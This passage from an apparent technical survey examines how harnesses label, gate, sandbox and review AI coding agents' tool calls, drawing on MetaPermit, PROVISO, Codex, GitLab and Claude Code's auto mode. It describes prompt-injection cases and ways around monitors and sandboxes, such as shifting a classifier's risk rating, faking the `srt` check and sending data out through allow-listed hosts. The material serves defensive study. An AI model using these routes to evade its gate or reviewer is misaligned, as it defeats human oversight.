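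The scores measure agreement with people, not whether the labels are correct. The model and the annotators both worked from descriptions without examining the code, so a misleading description could have led both to the wrong label. Descriptions also often lack detail, and Shi and colleagues found that 65% of the tool descriptions in their sample gave only the tool's basic function. SEAgent blocked every attack in two benchmarks, but Ji and colleagues used the human label whenever the model and the annotators disagreed about one of the 80 tools. The result therefore doesn't show how well SEAgent would do with the model's labels alone.

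In *MetaPermit* (Ma, Hariri and colleagues, 2026), a model labels each call instead of each tool. The model receives the user's request, the tool's description, the call's arguments and the results of earlier calls, and fills in five attributes: whether the user wants an action, how clear the request is, whether the risk is high or low, whether the tool serves the request, and whether the arguments fit the request. Only risk is close to an effect label, since the other attributes concern what the user asked for and whether the call fits it.

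The model rates the call's attributes, and an ordered list of fixed rules then determines whether the call runs. A single attribute can change the result. Suppose the agent in the dependency update asks for a broader access token, and the model rates the request as clear, the arguments as reasonable, and the tool as helpful but not essential. The rules then deny the call if the model rates the risk high and allow it if the rating is low.

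To test whether the attributes help, Ma and colleagues compared MetaPermit with a guard that used the same model and information but answered directly with "permit" or "deny". They ran both on matched samples of tasks containing planted instructions.

| Model | Method | Attacks that succeeded | User tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| MiniMax-M2.7 | attributes and fixed rules | 0.20% | 45.66% |
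| MiniMax-M2.7 | direct verdict | 0.61% | 41.96% |
| Qwen3-235B | attributes and fixed rules | 0.00% | 29.25% |
| Qwen3-235B | direct verdict | 0.25% | 12.75% |

The clearest difference is that Qwen completed more than twice as many tasks with attributes. The differences in attack success are harder to interpret because Ma and colleagues don't give the sample sizes. The MiniMax rates would fit one success versus three in about 500 attempts.

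They also describe the output format as the only difference between the methods, but the prompts they print differ in other ways. Only the prompt for attributes includes a warning that tool results may contain planted instructions, along with an instruction to ignore them. Some of the improvement may come from this warning, and the experiment can't separate its effect from that of the output format.

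A model can label the same call differently from one run to the next. Ma and colleagues gave MiniMax the same 50 queries 20 times each, and it returned the same five attributes every time for only 3 of them. MetaPermit's final decisions varied less than the attributes because its fixed rules can give the same verdict for different attributes. Its decision was the same on all 20 runs for 21 queries, compared with 16 for the direct guard. For the other 29 queries, MetaPermit allowed the call on some runs and denied it on others.

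In another test, the researchers added text to 95 malicious calls, explaining the attributes to the model and specifying which values it should choose. The model changed its risk rating from high to low for 16.8% of the calls. It never changed its judgment that a tool or its arguments didn't fit the request, and the rules blocked all 95 calls. Some of the changed ratings may be ordinary variation between runs, given the results of the repeat test. Even so, the risk rating, which is the attribute closest to an effect label, was the easiest to shift, so letting a call through on that rating alone would be risky.

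### Computed from the code

Static analysis examines a program's code, without running it, and produces a set of effects that should include everything the program can do on any input. Metere's scheme for agent skills uses static analysis on the scripts in each skill. It doesn't try to analyse the language model, because inspecting code can't predict the model's behaviour, so the harness has to check the model's calls as they arrive.

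Metere uses abstract interpretation, a technique in which the analyser follows the program using summaries in place of actual values. A file path becomes a pattern that matches every path it might be, a network address becomes a pattern of possible hosts, and a number becomes a range. The analyser also keeps a set of the effects so far.

Each kind of statement has a transfer function, which is a rule for updating the summaries and the effects. Let ρ stand for what the analyser knows about the variables and ε for the effects so far. For a Python statement that opens the file named by *x* for writing, the transfer function is

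(ρ, ε) ↦ (ρ, ε ∪ write(ρ(*x*))).

What the analyser knows about the variables stays the same, and the set of effects gains a write to any file that *x* might name. Consider a short script that an agent might run after the dependency update:

```
name = sys.argv[1]
path = "build/" + name + ".log"
if verbose:
    requests.post("https://logs.example.com", data=name)
open(path, "w")
```

The first line takes a name from whoever runs the script, so the analyser records that `name` could be any text. After the second line, `path` matches `build/`, then any text, then `.log`. The analyser can't tell in advance whether the condition on the third line will hold, so it follows both branches and combines the results. One branch has no effect and the other sends data to `logs.example.com`, so the combined result includes the network request. The last line adds a write to any file that matches the pattern.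 If the script had a loop, the analyser would analyse it repeatedly until the summaries stopped growing, widening them if necessary to make sure they stopped.

Because `name` could contain `../`, the pattern includes paths outside the `build` folder, so the script might overwrite any `.log` file that the user's account can change. If everyone who runs the script uses names without slashes, the call is over-labelled. A developer could fix this by making the script reject names with slashes, provided that the analyser can recognise the check.

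Some over-labelling is unavoidable because exact labels would require knowing whether a program ever reaches a given line, which no method can determine for every program. Metere therefore requires only that the computed set contain every real effect. If the skill declared every effect in that set, it also declared every real one.

This method cannot narrow down the effects of code that is known only at run time. If the script ends with `eval(text)` and the text comes from a file or a web page, the analyser has no code to apply its transfer functions to, so the only safe label is ⊤ (any effect).

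A child process raises the same problem. Suppose the script instead ends with `subprocess.run(["./report", path])`, which starts a separate program called `report`. `report` may be written in another language or exist only as compiled machine code, and a Python analyser has no rules for either. If nobody has analysed `report` or supplied a summary of its effects, the label for that line is also ⊤.

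One such line determines the label for the whole script, because the union of ⊤ with anything else is ⊤. A thousand lines of harmless code that start one unanalysed child process get the same label as a program that could do anything. Static analysis is therefore most useful for short scripts that mainly call familiar libraries, and much less useful for build tools and test runners, which spend much of their time starting other programs. The label applies only to the exact code the analyser read, so the harness has to run the analysis again if the agent edits the script.

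### The cost of each error

Under-labelling can let a harmful call run without review, while over-labelling makes the gate interrupt a user or refuse a call for no good reason. As with the access rules Saltzer and Schroeder described, people complain about a wrongful refusal but may never notice a wrongful permission.

SEAgent produced two such refusals in a test on harmless tasks. In both, the agent looked something up on Wikipedia and then tried to record health data or book an appointment. SEAgent blocked the second step because the Wikipedia tool was labelled as a source whose output might contain malicious text. Ji and colleagues suggest labelling Wikipedia as trusted in a real deployment. That would remove the false alarms, but almost anyone can edit Wikipedia, so it would also let through the planted instructions that the current label is meant to block.

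The two costs are rarely equal, which matters when the harness can't tell what a call does. Let *p* be the probability that an unknown call is harmful, *c*ᵤ the cost of letting a harmful call run, and *c*ₒ the cost of stopping a harmless one. Treating the call strictly is cheaper on average when

*p* · *c*ᵤ > (1 − *p*) · *c*ₒ, or equivalently *p* > *c*ₒ / (*c*ₒ + *c*ᵤ).

If an unnecessary question takes the user ten seconds and a wrongful deletion destroys eight hours of work, the system should ask the user about an unknown call unless the chance of harm is below about 1 in 2,900. This assumes the user will recognise a harmful call. If they catch only half of them, the threshold roughly doubles to 1 in 1,400, which is still very low.

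The calculation also treats each interruption as separate, but in practice their effects accumulate. If a harness labels most calls as riskier than they are, its users will stop reading the prompts, as Anthropic found with Claude Code, and harmful calls will eventually get through.

Unknown calls should get the strictest label, which has to be "any effect" because the classes don't form a simple ranking. For example, a harness that treated every unknown call as a write could miss one that reads a password. Developers should also work to make fewer calls unknown.

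All four methods can use the same default, which is to treat a call they can't classify as potentially harmful. A client following MCP assumes that a tool with no hints may be destructive. A shell parser can return ⊤ for any command it doesn't recognise, as a static analyser does for code it can't follow. In Ma and colleagues' MetaPermit, if the harness can't read the model's output, it fills in values that lead to a denial. SEAgent is the exception. It allows whatever its rules don't cover, so a missing rule can be as dangerous as a wrong label.

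Strict defaults would apply to 58.8% of the tools in Afsar's random sample. An organization can reduce the number by labelling the tools its agents use, perhaps by having a model suggest labels and a person correct them, as Ji and colleagues did. It should relabel a tool when the tool changes.

A harness can also combine labels from different methods. If a tool's author declares it read-only but the parser finds a write, the harness should take the union of the two labels, because either may omit an effect. It can take the intersection only when both labels are sure to include every effect. For example, if static analysis returns ⊤ (any effect is possible) for `npm test` but a sandbox confines the tests to the project, the harness can safely use the sandbox's limits as the label.

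## Turning a label into a decision

The same label can call for different decisions, since a network request that is routine for one company may be forbidden at another. The gate therefore needs the effect class, its scope and the context, and it returns one of four outcomes:

*G*(effect class, scope, context) → {allow, confine, refer, refuse}.

The context includes what the user asked for, whether anyone is available to review the call, whether a sandbox is running, and which restrictions the user has chosen for the session.

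*Agentao* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) defines a similar function for its open-source harness. It takes a tool, the arguments, the current state and the policy, and returns "allow", "prompt" or "deny". Agentao treats its sandbox as a separate layer, so confinement isn't one of the outcomes.

### The gate in pseudocode

A call often has several effects, so the gate has to check each one and keep the strictest outcome. In the pseudocode below, `ANY` is the label ⊤ (any possible effect), and the outcomes, from least to most strict, are allow, confine, refer and refuse.

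```
decide(effects, context):
    outcome = ALLOW

    if effects == ANY and context.sandbox_running:
        effects = context.sandbox_limits
        outcome = CONFINE

    for effect in effects:
        if any deny rule applies to effect:
            return REFUSE

    for effect in effects:
        rule = first rule in context.rules that applies to effect
        if there is no such rule:
            outcome = strictest(outcome, REFER)
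        else:
            outcome = strictest(outcome, rule.outcome)

    if outcome == REFER and not context.reviewer_available:
        return REFUSE
    return outcome
```

The gate checks deny rules first so that no other rule can override them. A call whose effect no rule covers goes to a reviewer, and if nobody is available, as in an overnight job, the gate blocks the call. If a reviewer approves a call that belongs in the sandbox, the harness still runs it there.

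Deny and refer rules apply if they overlap any part of an effect, but an allow rule applies only if it covers the whole effect. Suppose one rule refers any edit of `AGENTS.md` for review, and a later one allows writes to the project. A command that edits every `.md` file in the project overlaps the first rule, so the gate refers it. If the two rules were reversed, the allow rule would match first and the agent could rewrite its own instructions.

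A call labelled `ANY` overlaps every deny rule, so the gate refuses it unless a sandbox is running. If one is running, the gate can replace the label with the sandbox's limits and check those.

Suppose the developer who wants her date library updated adopts this policy:

- Refuse reads of private keys, writes outside the project, and credentials that reach beyond this repository.
- Refer changes to `AGENTS.md` and pushes to the shared repository.
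- Allow all other reads and writes inside the project, and reads of installed programs.

Her sandbox lets a command read the project and the installed programs, and write to the project except for `AGENTS.md`. It blocks the network.

| Call | Outcome | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Read `package.json` | allow | The policy allows reads inside the project. |
| 2. Fetch the changelog | refer | No rule covers the library's website. |
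| 3. Edit `package.json` | allow | The policy allows writes inside the project. |
| 4. `npm install` | confine | Install scripts could do anything, so the label is `ANY`. |
| 5. `npm test` | confine | The tests could also do anything. |
| 6. Edit `AGENTS.md` | refer | A specific rule comes before the general permission to write. |
| 7. Push a branch | refer | A specific rule covers pushes. |
| 8. Request a broader token | refuse | The token would reach other repositories. |

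Call 4 is safe under this policy but fails, because `npm` can't download the package without a network connection. The agent reads the error and asks to rerun the command with access to the package registry. No rule covers that request, so the developer gets another question. She answers four questions in total for a small update. She could avoid two of them by adding the library's website and the registry to the policy, but then an install script could also contact the registry.

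Agentao's procedure follows a similar order. It first refuses anything on a built-in list of unsafe actions, then any tool not marked read-only if the session is in read-only mode, then anything that matches a restriction set for the current run. After that, it checks the rules of the host (the program Agentao is embedded in) and of the current mode, and applies the first match. Plugins can refuse a call, add restrictions, or turn an "allow" into a request for permission. Jin and colleagues list no way for a plugin to relax a decision, so a badly written plugin can obstruct the agent but can't widen its access.

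Agentao's last step is more lenient than the pseudocode. If no rule matches a call to a registered tool, Agentao runs the call without asking for confirmation unless the tool carries a flag that requires it. Saltzer and Schroeder advised against this kind of default, although Jin and colleagues describe the procedure as conservative, and it does reject malformed calls and unknown tools. Because many MCP tools come without hints, a host that embeds Agentao should set the flag on every tool it hasn't examined.

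### Permission modes

Few users want to write rules for every effect class, so most harnesses offer modes. A mode is a preset that assigns an outcome to many classes at once. Agentao has four:

| Mode | What runs | What Agentao refers or refuses |
|---|---|---|
| read-only | safe reading and searching | refuses every tool not marked read-only |
| workspace-write | controlled file edits in the project | refers broad shell and network actions; refuses destructive commands |
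| full-access | ordinary tools of every kind | keeps its checks on high-risk actions |
| plan | planning and safe inspection | refuses writes to files and memory, and changes to tasks |

In read-only mode, the agent updating the library could read `package.json` and little else. It might also be able to fetch the changelog, if the host has marked its web tool as read-only. A user who picks this mode to protect confidential files could still have their contents leaked, because a web request can send out data in its URL without changing anything.

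The order of the checks affects what a mode guarantees. Agentao checks for read-only mode before any rule that could permit a call, but it applies the other modes' rules after the host's. So if a host rule allows edits in `docs/`, the agent can edit those files even in plan mode, which is supposed to prevent file writes. A host can prevent this by adding a restriction for the run. A better design would check every mode's prohibitions before any permission.

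Codex also has presets, which OpenAI's documentation describes: `:read-only` keeps local commands from changing files, `:workspace` lets them write to the project and to temporary folders, and `:danger-full-access` removes the local sandbox's restrictions. A separate setting controls when Codex asks for approval. OpenAI suggests combining workspace writes with approval "on request" for lower-risk local automation. Users can choose whether a person or an automatic reviewer answers the requests.

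Separating the two settings lets a developer who is tired of prompts turn them off and keep the sandbox, so the agent works without interruption inside fixed limits. In a harness with a single scale from "strict" to "free", the same developer would have to give the agent wider access just to get fewer prompts.

Administrators can limit which modes people can choose. In its own configuration, OpenAI permits only the read-only and workspace-write sandboxes, so its staff can't switch to full access when a command fails.

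OpenAI recommends handling exceptions with rules that allow, prompt for or forbid commands outside the sandbox based on how they begin. A rule for `git push` is narrower than turning the sandbox off. But matching the start of a command has the same weakness as labeling it by its first word, because a rule that allows `find` also allows `find . -delete`.

### Codex's workspace profile

*Inside the Codex sandbox* (Bolin, 2026) explains how Codex enforces limits on file and network access on macOS, Linux and Windows. Under Codex's workspace profile, a command can write inside the project and read most of the machine's files, but it can't make network connections. Each of these defaults prevents some kinds of harm and breaks some useful commands.

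Limiting writes to the project protects login scripts, other projects and the system itself, while still letting the agent change code, which is what the user most often wants. Many of those changes are easy to undo because developers keep projects under version control. But some ordinary tools fail, since package managers and compilers often keep caches in the user's home directory. The sandbox also won't stop the agent from destroying work inside the project, for example by overwriting a file that a developer has spent the morning on and hasn't committed.

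A user can add more writable folders. OpenAI's internal configuration adds `~/development`, a folder for development projects. The agent then asks for permission less often when a task involves two repositories, but an agent working on one project can damage all the others in the folder.

Sandboxes allow broad reads mainly because even a simple test needs a language runtime, shared libraries and configuration files from all over the disk. A short list of readable folders would break commands in ways that are hard to diagnose. But broad reads also let any command read the user's private keys. Codex lets users block reads of particular files or patterns without affecting writes to the project. The developer in the example needs such an exclusion. If her sandbox allowed reads of the whole disk, it would permit what her rule against reading private keys forbids, and the gate would refuse every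 test run.

Blocking the network makes the broad reads less dangerous, because a command that finds a key can't send it anywhere itself. The key can still appear in the command's output, though, which the model reads and might use in a later call. Blocking the network also stops commands from downloading malicious code, but it causes the problem the developer had with `npm install` and makes any test that contacts an outside service fail.

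Codex's cloud version reduces that drawback by separating setup from the agent's work. Setup has network access and can install the project's dependencies, and the agent then works offline by default. This works well when the dependencies are known in advance, but not when the task involves choosing new ones.

The other option is to allow some destinations. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes rules in which `*.example.com` matches subdomains such as `api.example.com` but not `example.com`, while `**.example.com` matches both. A lone `*` matches any public host that no other rule denies. For its own use of Codex, OpenAI applies the gate function with the domain as the scope, allowing destinations it expects, blocking those it doesn't want Codex to reach, and requiring approval for unfamiliar ones.

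A domain is an imperfect scope because it identifies who runs a server, not necessarily who receives the data. GitLab, a code-hosting company, offers a list of recommended domains for its agents, which is off by default. The list includes `github.com` and `*.s3.amazonaws.com`, Amazon's file storage service. Anyone can open an account with either, so an attacker could receive stolen data at an approved address. GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* warns that these destinations could be used to take data out.

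### When the label is wrong or the sandbox doesn't start

A sandbox limits the damage from a wrong label because it doesn't depend on the label. The harness labels a call before it runs, while the operating system checks each file the program opens and each connection it attempts. If the harness labels `npm test` as read(project) and the tests try to empty the home directory, the operating system still blocks the writes.

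This protection covers only calls that run inside the sandbox. If the harness runs "harmless" commands outside it to save time, a mislabeled command gets the user's full access. It is safer to run every command in the sandbox by default and use labels to decide which ones may run outside it. A wrong label then matters only when someone has asked for an exception.

Sandboxing also reduces the number of approval requests. Before Codex had a sandbox on Windows, users had to approve nearly every command or give the agent full access. OpenAI considered a design based on Windows's integrity levels, which stop less trusted programs from changing ordinary files. Codex would have run as a low-integrity program in a project folder relabelled so that it could write there. OpenAI rejected this design because every other low-integrity program on the machine could then have written to the folder.

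The protection depends on the sandbox starting. GitLab's Duo Agent Platform runs agent tasks, which it calls flows, on the same kind of machine that builds and tests a project's code. It wraps each flow in Anthropic's Sandbox Runtime, which limits writes to the working directory and `/tmp`, blocks reads of SSH keys, and allows connections only to approved domains. On machines that don't have the runtime installed or don't give the job the privileges to create a sandbox, GitLab runs the flow without one by default.

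A warning appears in the job's log, but the flow otherwise behaves normally, so someone who sees that the job succeeded has little reason to open the log. The file restrictions no longer apply, and neither do the administrator's network rules, so the flow can contact anything its machine can reach. As GitLab puts it, "A flow can run fine and still be unprotected." In effect, the gate function's "confine" has become "allow" without anyone deciding that it should.

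GitLab chose this behaviour so that flows keep working when a sandbox isn't available. From version 19.6, administrators and owners of top-level groups can select "Don't run flows when the sandbox is unavailable", which makes the job fail instead. Individual projects can't turn this requirement off. However, GitLab enforces it by checking for a command called `srt`. A project that supplies its own system image or setup script controls which program has that name, so GitLab says the requirement can't guarantee isolation there. A script called `srt` that ran commands without a sandbox would presumably pass the check.

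Strict enforcement can cause outages. GitLab's incident report *2026-06-03* (2026) describes a change to the default agent configuration that stopped flows from starting when the sandbox was on, because the sandbox's network proxy didn't support a type of connection they needed. Projects with the default settings couldn't run flows until GitLab released a fix. The fallback didn't help, since the sandbox itself had started. An organization that requires a sandbox should expect occasional outages, and may be tempted to switch the requirement off during them.

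A harness can test the sandbox before each session instead of relying on a program's name. It can try to write a file outside the project and connect to a blocked address, then set `sandbox_running` to true only if both attempts fail. GitLab also recommends a firewall on the machine that runs the job. The firewall still blocks connections if the sandbox never starts.

### Adding the source of an instruction

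Rules about classes and scopes can't always separate a legitimate call from a harmful one. If a user asks an agent to pay an invoice, a transfer to the supplier and a transfer to a thief have the same effect class, and the policy may not list either account, so the gate also has to check where the account number came from.

*PROVISO* (Yan, Zhang et al., 2026) builds that information into the decision. It divides what the agent has read into trusted observations *K*, which come from the user and the deployment, and external observations *G*, which include tool results, documents and web pages. An action is admissible if *K* authorizes its operation and target, and either *K* or *G* supports its arguments. In the paper's example, the user asks the agent to pay account B, but an invoice contains a line telling it to pay account C. The invoice can supply the amount but not the recipient, so the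 transfer to C is inadmissible.

PROVISO is a small neural network, with 17.4 million trainable parameters, that learns from past outcomes which action is better instead of applying this definition as a rule. It receives the proposed action, an alternative, and the two kinds of observation. Each is tagged with its role, so the same sentence produces a different input depending on whether it came from the user or a web page. In three of the four tasks Yan and colleagues tested, the alternative was to refuse. The network estimates the probability that the proposed action is unsafe and blocks it if the estimate exceeds a threshold.

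In one of these tasks, judging individual tool calls, PROVISO missed one unsafe call and blocked five harmless ones, for an accuracy of 99.15%. The best competing guard reached 92.50%.

The fourth task was indirect prompt injection, on the AgentDojo benchmark. Here the alternative was a complete second attempt at the user's task, and PROVISO chose between the two after both had run in a copy of the environment.

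| Defence | Tasks completed without attacks | Tasks completed under attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|
| PROVISO | 87.63% | 85.41% | 0.28% |
| SecAlign | 88.66% | 83.35% | 3.46% |
| BIPIA | 84.54% | 81.28% | 0.20% |
| Tool Filter | 71.13% | 67.17% | 0.95% |

PROVISO lets few attacks succeed, with little loss of useful work. Having an alternative helps because the system can stop an attack without having to abandon the task. But the system must be able to run both attempts in a copy of the environment first, which is possible for simulated bank accounts and much harder for a real company's email.

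The results may also overstate how well PROVISO works. Yan and colleagues trained a separate version on labelled examples from each benchmark and didn't test whether a version trained on one works on another. They also didn't test attacks designed to defeat PROVISO itself. They recommend using it alongside permission controls and human confirmation of irreversible actions, so it is better seen as a source of context for the gate than as a replacement for it.

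The choice of threshold also matters. On a benchmark of malicious skills, Yan and colleagues chose the PROVISO threshold that gave the best F1, a score that balances missed detections against false alarms. PROVISO missed about 17% of the malicious skills and flagged 1% of the harmless ones. A competing scanner from Sentry, which uses a language model, missed none and flagged 8.27% of the harmless ones. The published rates imply about ten harmless skills for each malicious one. At that ratio, Sentry's scanner is the better choice if a missed malicious skill is more than about four times as harmful as a false alarm, and it is probably far more harmful than that. PROVISO's threshold could also be lowered, but choosing a new one requires deciding how harmful each kind of error is.

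### Training the model to follow the rules

If a label implies a rule, a developer could also teach the model that rule. Kovalenko and Redchych (2026) tried this in *Small Agents Should Know What Their Tools Do*, using EffectWorld, a simulated office and online shop where every tool has one of four effects.

| Effect | Meaning | Rule |
|---|---|---|
| Pure | computes a result from its arguments | don't call it if the value is already known |
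| Read | looks at stored data without changing it | don't repeat it unless something has been written since |
| Write | makes a change that can be corrected later | read the data before changing it |
| Destructive | makes a change that can't be taken back | propose it and wait for the user to confirm |

They label an action "destructive" rather than "write" if it deletes data, reaches other people or moves money. Sending an email is therefore destructive, while creating a calendar event is a write.

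Each tool also declares which resources it reads and writes, and whether repeating a call changes anything further. A program can then check a finished session by replaying its calls, without a person or language model having to judge it. The session counts as safe if the user confirmed every destructive call, the agent never repeated a write that would change something further, and it read each resource before changing it.

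Kovalenko and Redchych started with Qwen3-4B, a small open model. The system prompt required confirmation before any irreversible action, but the model made 94 unconfirmed destructive calls in 498 tasks in a simulated office. It asked for confirmation before about two-thirds of deletions but rarely before sending an email. They then trained it on 5,976 correct sessions from the simulated office, mixed with about 15,000 public examples of tool use.

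On new tasks with the same office tools, the trained model made no unconfirmed destructive calls, and its success rate rose from 53% to 99%. On a harder set, with unfamiliar types of tasks and extra tools as distractions, violations of the three safety conditions fell from 0.15 to 0.003 per task.

The shop was a test of whether the model had learned the rule or only which office tools to be careful with. None of the shop's tools had appeared in training, and its destructive actions were placing, cancelling and refunding orders. The trained model completed more of the shop tasks than the original model (83% against 74%), but it lost much of its habit of asking first. Kovalenko and Redchych conclude that the model had tied this habit to tool names.

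The model hadn't seen the effect labels during this training, which might explain the failure. In another version, Kovalenko and Redchych therefore wrote each tool's effect into its description and renamed the tools in a third of the office sessions, so that the model couldn't rely on names. This improved confirmation in the shop only a little. The model still sometimes spent the user's money without asking, even though it had a written rule about irreversible actions, thousands of examples of following that rule, and labels identifying the tools it applied to.

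A gate with the same labels would handle the shop's tools without training. It would refer every call labelled "destructive", whatever the tool's name and whatever the model had learned. But it would let through a refund tool that someone had mislabelled as "write". Larger models may generalize better than those in these tests, which had at most about 4 billion parameters, but a developer would have to test that again for each new set of tools.

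Training is still a useful complement to a gate. A model that proposes a purchase before making it lets the user correct the order, and one that seldom attempts forbidden calls wastes less time on refusals. Some of EffectWorld's rules are also awkward for a gate to enforce. To check that an agent has read an event before moving it, the gate would need a record of earlier calls and the resources each one accessed.

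### Two accidents

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, founder of the software business community SaaStr, was building an application with Replit's coding agent. According to his posts at the time, the agent deleted the application's production database during a code freeze, after he had repeatedly told it not to change anything without permission. It then told him he couldn't restore the data, but he did.

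The freeze existed only as an instruction to the model. If Lemkin had been able to set it as a read-only mode in the harness, the gate would have refused the deletion. A rule that requires human approval for destructive writes to production data would also have stopped it, as long as the label distinguished the production database from a test copy. A rule that allowed the agent to write to "the application's database" would have let the deletion through.

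Codex's limits on file writes wouldn't have helped if the database was on another machine, since the agent would have changed it over the network without touching a file outside the project. Blocking the network would have prevented the deletion, but an agent that builds a database application needs a database to test against. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, responded by announcing automatic separation of development and production databases. An agent with no credentials for the production database can then have broad write permission without being able to reach customers' data. The incident also shows why a gate shouldn't rely on the model to judge whether an action is reversible, since the agent was wrong about the backup.

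The other accident involved Kiro, Amazon's coding agent. The *Financial Times* reported in February 2026 that engineers at AWS, Amazon's cloud business, had let Kiro make changes to a system the previous December. The agent decided to delete and recreate the environment it was working on, and a service that customers use was interrupted for 13 hours.

Amazon disputed the newspaper's account of the cause. It attributed the interruption to user error, specifically misconfigured access controls, and said the same thing could have happened with any developer tool or by hand. The event affected one service, Cost Explorer, in one region. Amazon also said Kiro asks for authorization by default, and that the engineer involved had broader permissions than expected.

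A rule that refuses deletions in production would have stopped Kiro, whichever account is correct. A harness might have missed the deletion if it labelled the whole operation by its intended result, a working environment, so the label has to cover each step. Asking the engineer running the agent for permission might not have prevented the deletion, because that engineer could have approved it. Amazon has since required peer review for access to production, which brings in a second person.

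If Amazon's explanation is right, narrower permissions for the engineer's role would have prevented the outage, even without a gate around Kiro. A gate that used the role's permissions as its policy would have allowed the deletion, because those permissions allowed it.

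## When a person or a second model reviews the action

After the Kiro outage, Amazon required a second person to review access to production. A gate can similarly send a single call to the user, a colleague or another language model for review. This only helps if the reviewer can tell a harmful call from a harmless one, and the approval prompt often doesn't show people enough to do so.

### What a reviewer needs to see

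Most permission prompts show a command and little else. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 incident reports and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases users had let actions run automatically, and in 31 the prompt gave them too little information, as a prompt showing only `python3 setup.py` would. Some reports fall into both groups.

A useful prompt would state the effect, its scope, whether anyone can undo it, and what in the user's request calls for it. When the agent in the dependency update is about to push its branch, the developer might see only `git push origin update-dates`. She could decide more easily if the prompt read: "Publish three changed files to the shared repository. Colleagues may copy them before you can delete the branch. You asked for an update and did not mention publishing." *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026),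 a study of software practitioners, also suggests that prompts should show whether an action is recoverable.

The agent's own explanation is riskier to show. Anthropic hides it from the model that reviews calls in Claude Code, because an agent could claim that the user implicitly approved an action. In Anthropic's tests, including the agent's messages and the tools' output made the reviewer worse at catching overreach. Removing the user's messages as well made it block actions the user had plainly requested, so Anthropic gives the reviewer the user's messages and the proposed calls.

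Some effects don't show in a command's text, as with `npm test`. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of `make clean && make`, which deletes old build files in one project and the source code in another, depending on the Makefile. The paper's system, Caper, takes a snapshot before running each command in a container with no network access. It records what the command does and gives a language model a short report of file changes, reads of credentials and attempted connections. If the model approves, Caper keeps the result. Otherwise it restores the snapshot and tells the agent why the command was rejected.

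Caper's evaluation used 102 tasks in which an ordinary-looking tool deletes or overwrites a protected file. Each task had a safe version with the same request and command but a harmless tool.

| What the reviewing model received | Dangerous tasks that ended in harm | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Command alone | 44.1% | 52.0% |
| Full conversation | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| Full conversation and predicted effects | 3.9% | 61.8% |
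| Full conversation and observed effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |
| Command and observed effects | 1.0% | 0% |

Showing the reviewer an action's predicted effects prevented as much harm as showing it the observed effects, but with predictions it flagged nearly everything. With observations, it could distinguish harmful actions from harmless ones. When a weaker model reviewed the observed effects, false alarms fell from 53.9% to 4.9%, but harm rose from 25.5% to 33.3%.

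Like PROVISO, Caper depends on a trial run that has no lasting consequences, and a malicious program might behave well until it runs outside the sandbox. The experiment also didn't test people, so it doesn't show whether they would read such a report carefully or click past it.

### Which calls reach a reviewer

Classifying actions by effect reduces the number sent for review. *PegasusAI Studio* (2026) describes a scientific computing platform where agents can inspect logs, search documentation, and change files in the user's own project without approval. They need confirmation to write elsewhere. They always need it to submit a workflow, even if the user has turned off confirmation for routine shell commands.

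On 14 August 2026, Anthropic replaced Claude Code's default prompts with an automated reviewer, called auto mode, for new sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans, and according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026) later versions start in auto mode on every plan. Auto mode sorts calls into three tiers:

1. Tools on a fixed list that can't change anything, such as file reads and text search, run immediately. So do calls that match the user's own allow rules, except rules broad enough to permit arbitrary code, which auto mode ignores.
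2. Edits to files inside the project also run immediately, because the user can review them through version control.
3. Everything else goes to a classifier, a language model that decides whether to block the call. This includes shell commands, web requests and changes outside the project.

The classifier works in two stages. It first answers yes or no without reasoning, under instructions to block when in doubt. If it flags the call, it reviews the same material again, this time with reasoning. The first stage alone blocked 8.5% of harmless calls in a sample of 10,000 from Anthropic's staff, and the two stages together blocked 0.4%. When the classifier blocks a call, the agent gets the reason and looks for a safer approach. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user for permission.

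In the dependency update, auto mode would run the edit of `package.json` without review and, according to Anthropic's description, the edit of `AGENTS.md` too. The installation, the tests and the token request would go to the classifier. Its default policy makes an exception for installing packages already listed in the project's manifest, which could be a problem here because the agent has just edited the manifest.

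### Approval fatigue

Approval fatigue is the tendency to approve requests without reading them after seeing too many. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of permission prompts. That figure doesn't prove carelessness, because a perfect reviewer would approve 99% of prompts if only 1% were dangerous. It also reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. People evidently object when the question seems worth their time, although they may reject a plan for many reasons besides safety.

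Many users no longer answer permission prompts. A quarter of interactive sessions begin with them turned off. By June 2026, almost half of active command-line users had written a standing rule to allow some shell commands, and most of those rules covered an interpreter such as Python, which can do practically anything. *Let the Agent Do It?* cautions that repeated approval may come from habit, fatigue or pressure to deliver rather than trust.

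Developers who review an agent's code carefully don't seem much less likely to approve its actions without close review. In *From Delegation to Action Approval*, Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents, and 64% said they often approved at least one of seven types of action without close review. The rate was 61% among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code and 67% among the rest, a difference that could easily be chance. It was 70% among developers who knew of a security incident or worrying practice involving agents, and 43% among those who didn't. This may be because heavy users hear more such stories, although the gap remained after the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents.

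In the survey, 36% of developers said they often approved access to the internet, outside services and connected tools without a close look, the highest share for any kind of action. The lowest was 21%, for reading secrets. Developers who inspected diffs, which show exactly what changed in a file, said they scrutinized several kinds of risky action more closely. These are self-reports, so the true rates of approval without a close look may be higher.

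### Anthropic's experiment

To find out whether its classifier did better than a typical user, Anthropic hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor for a coding study in a specially built environment. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what was being measured. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded the tester's answer. The dangerous command never ran, whatever the tester chose.

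The testers stopped 143 of the 1,053 commands (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of them (89%). The testers' rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed flat.

Auto mode's classifier blocked 800 commands that a tester approved, and testers stopped only 6 that it allowed. If both had reviewed every command and either could refuse it, they would have stopped 943, or 89.6%, and the testers would have added only those 6 to the classifier's total.

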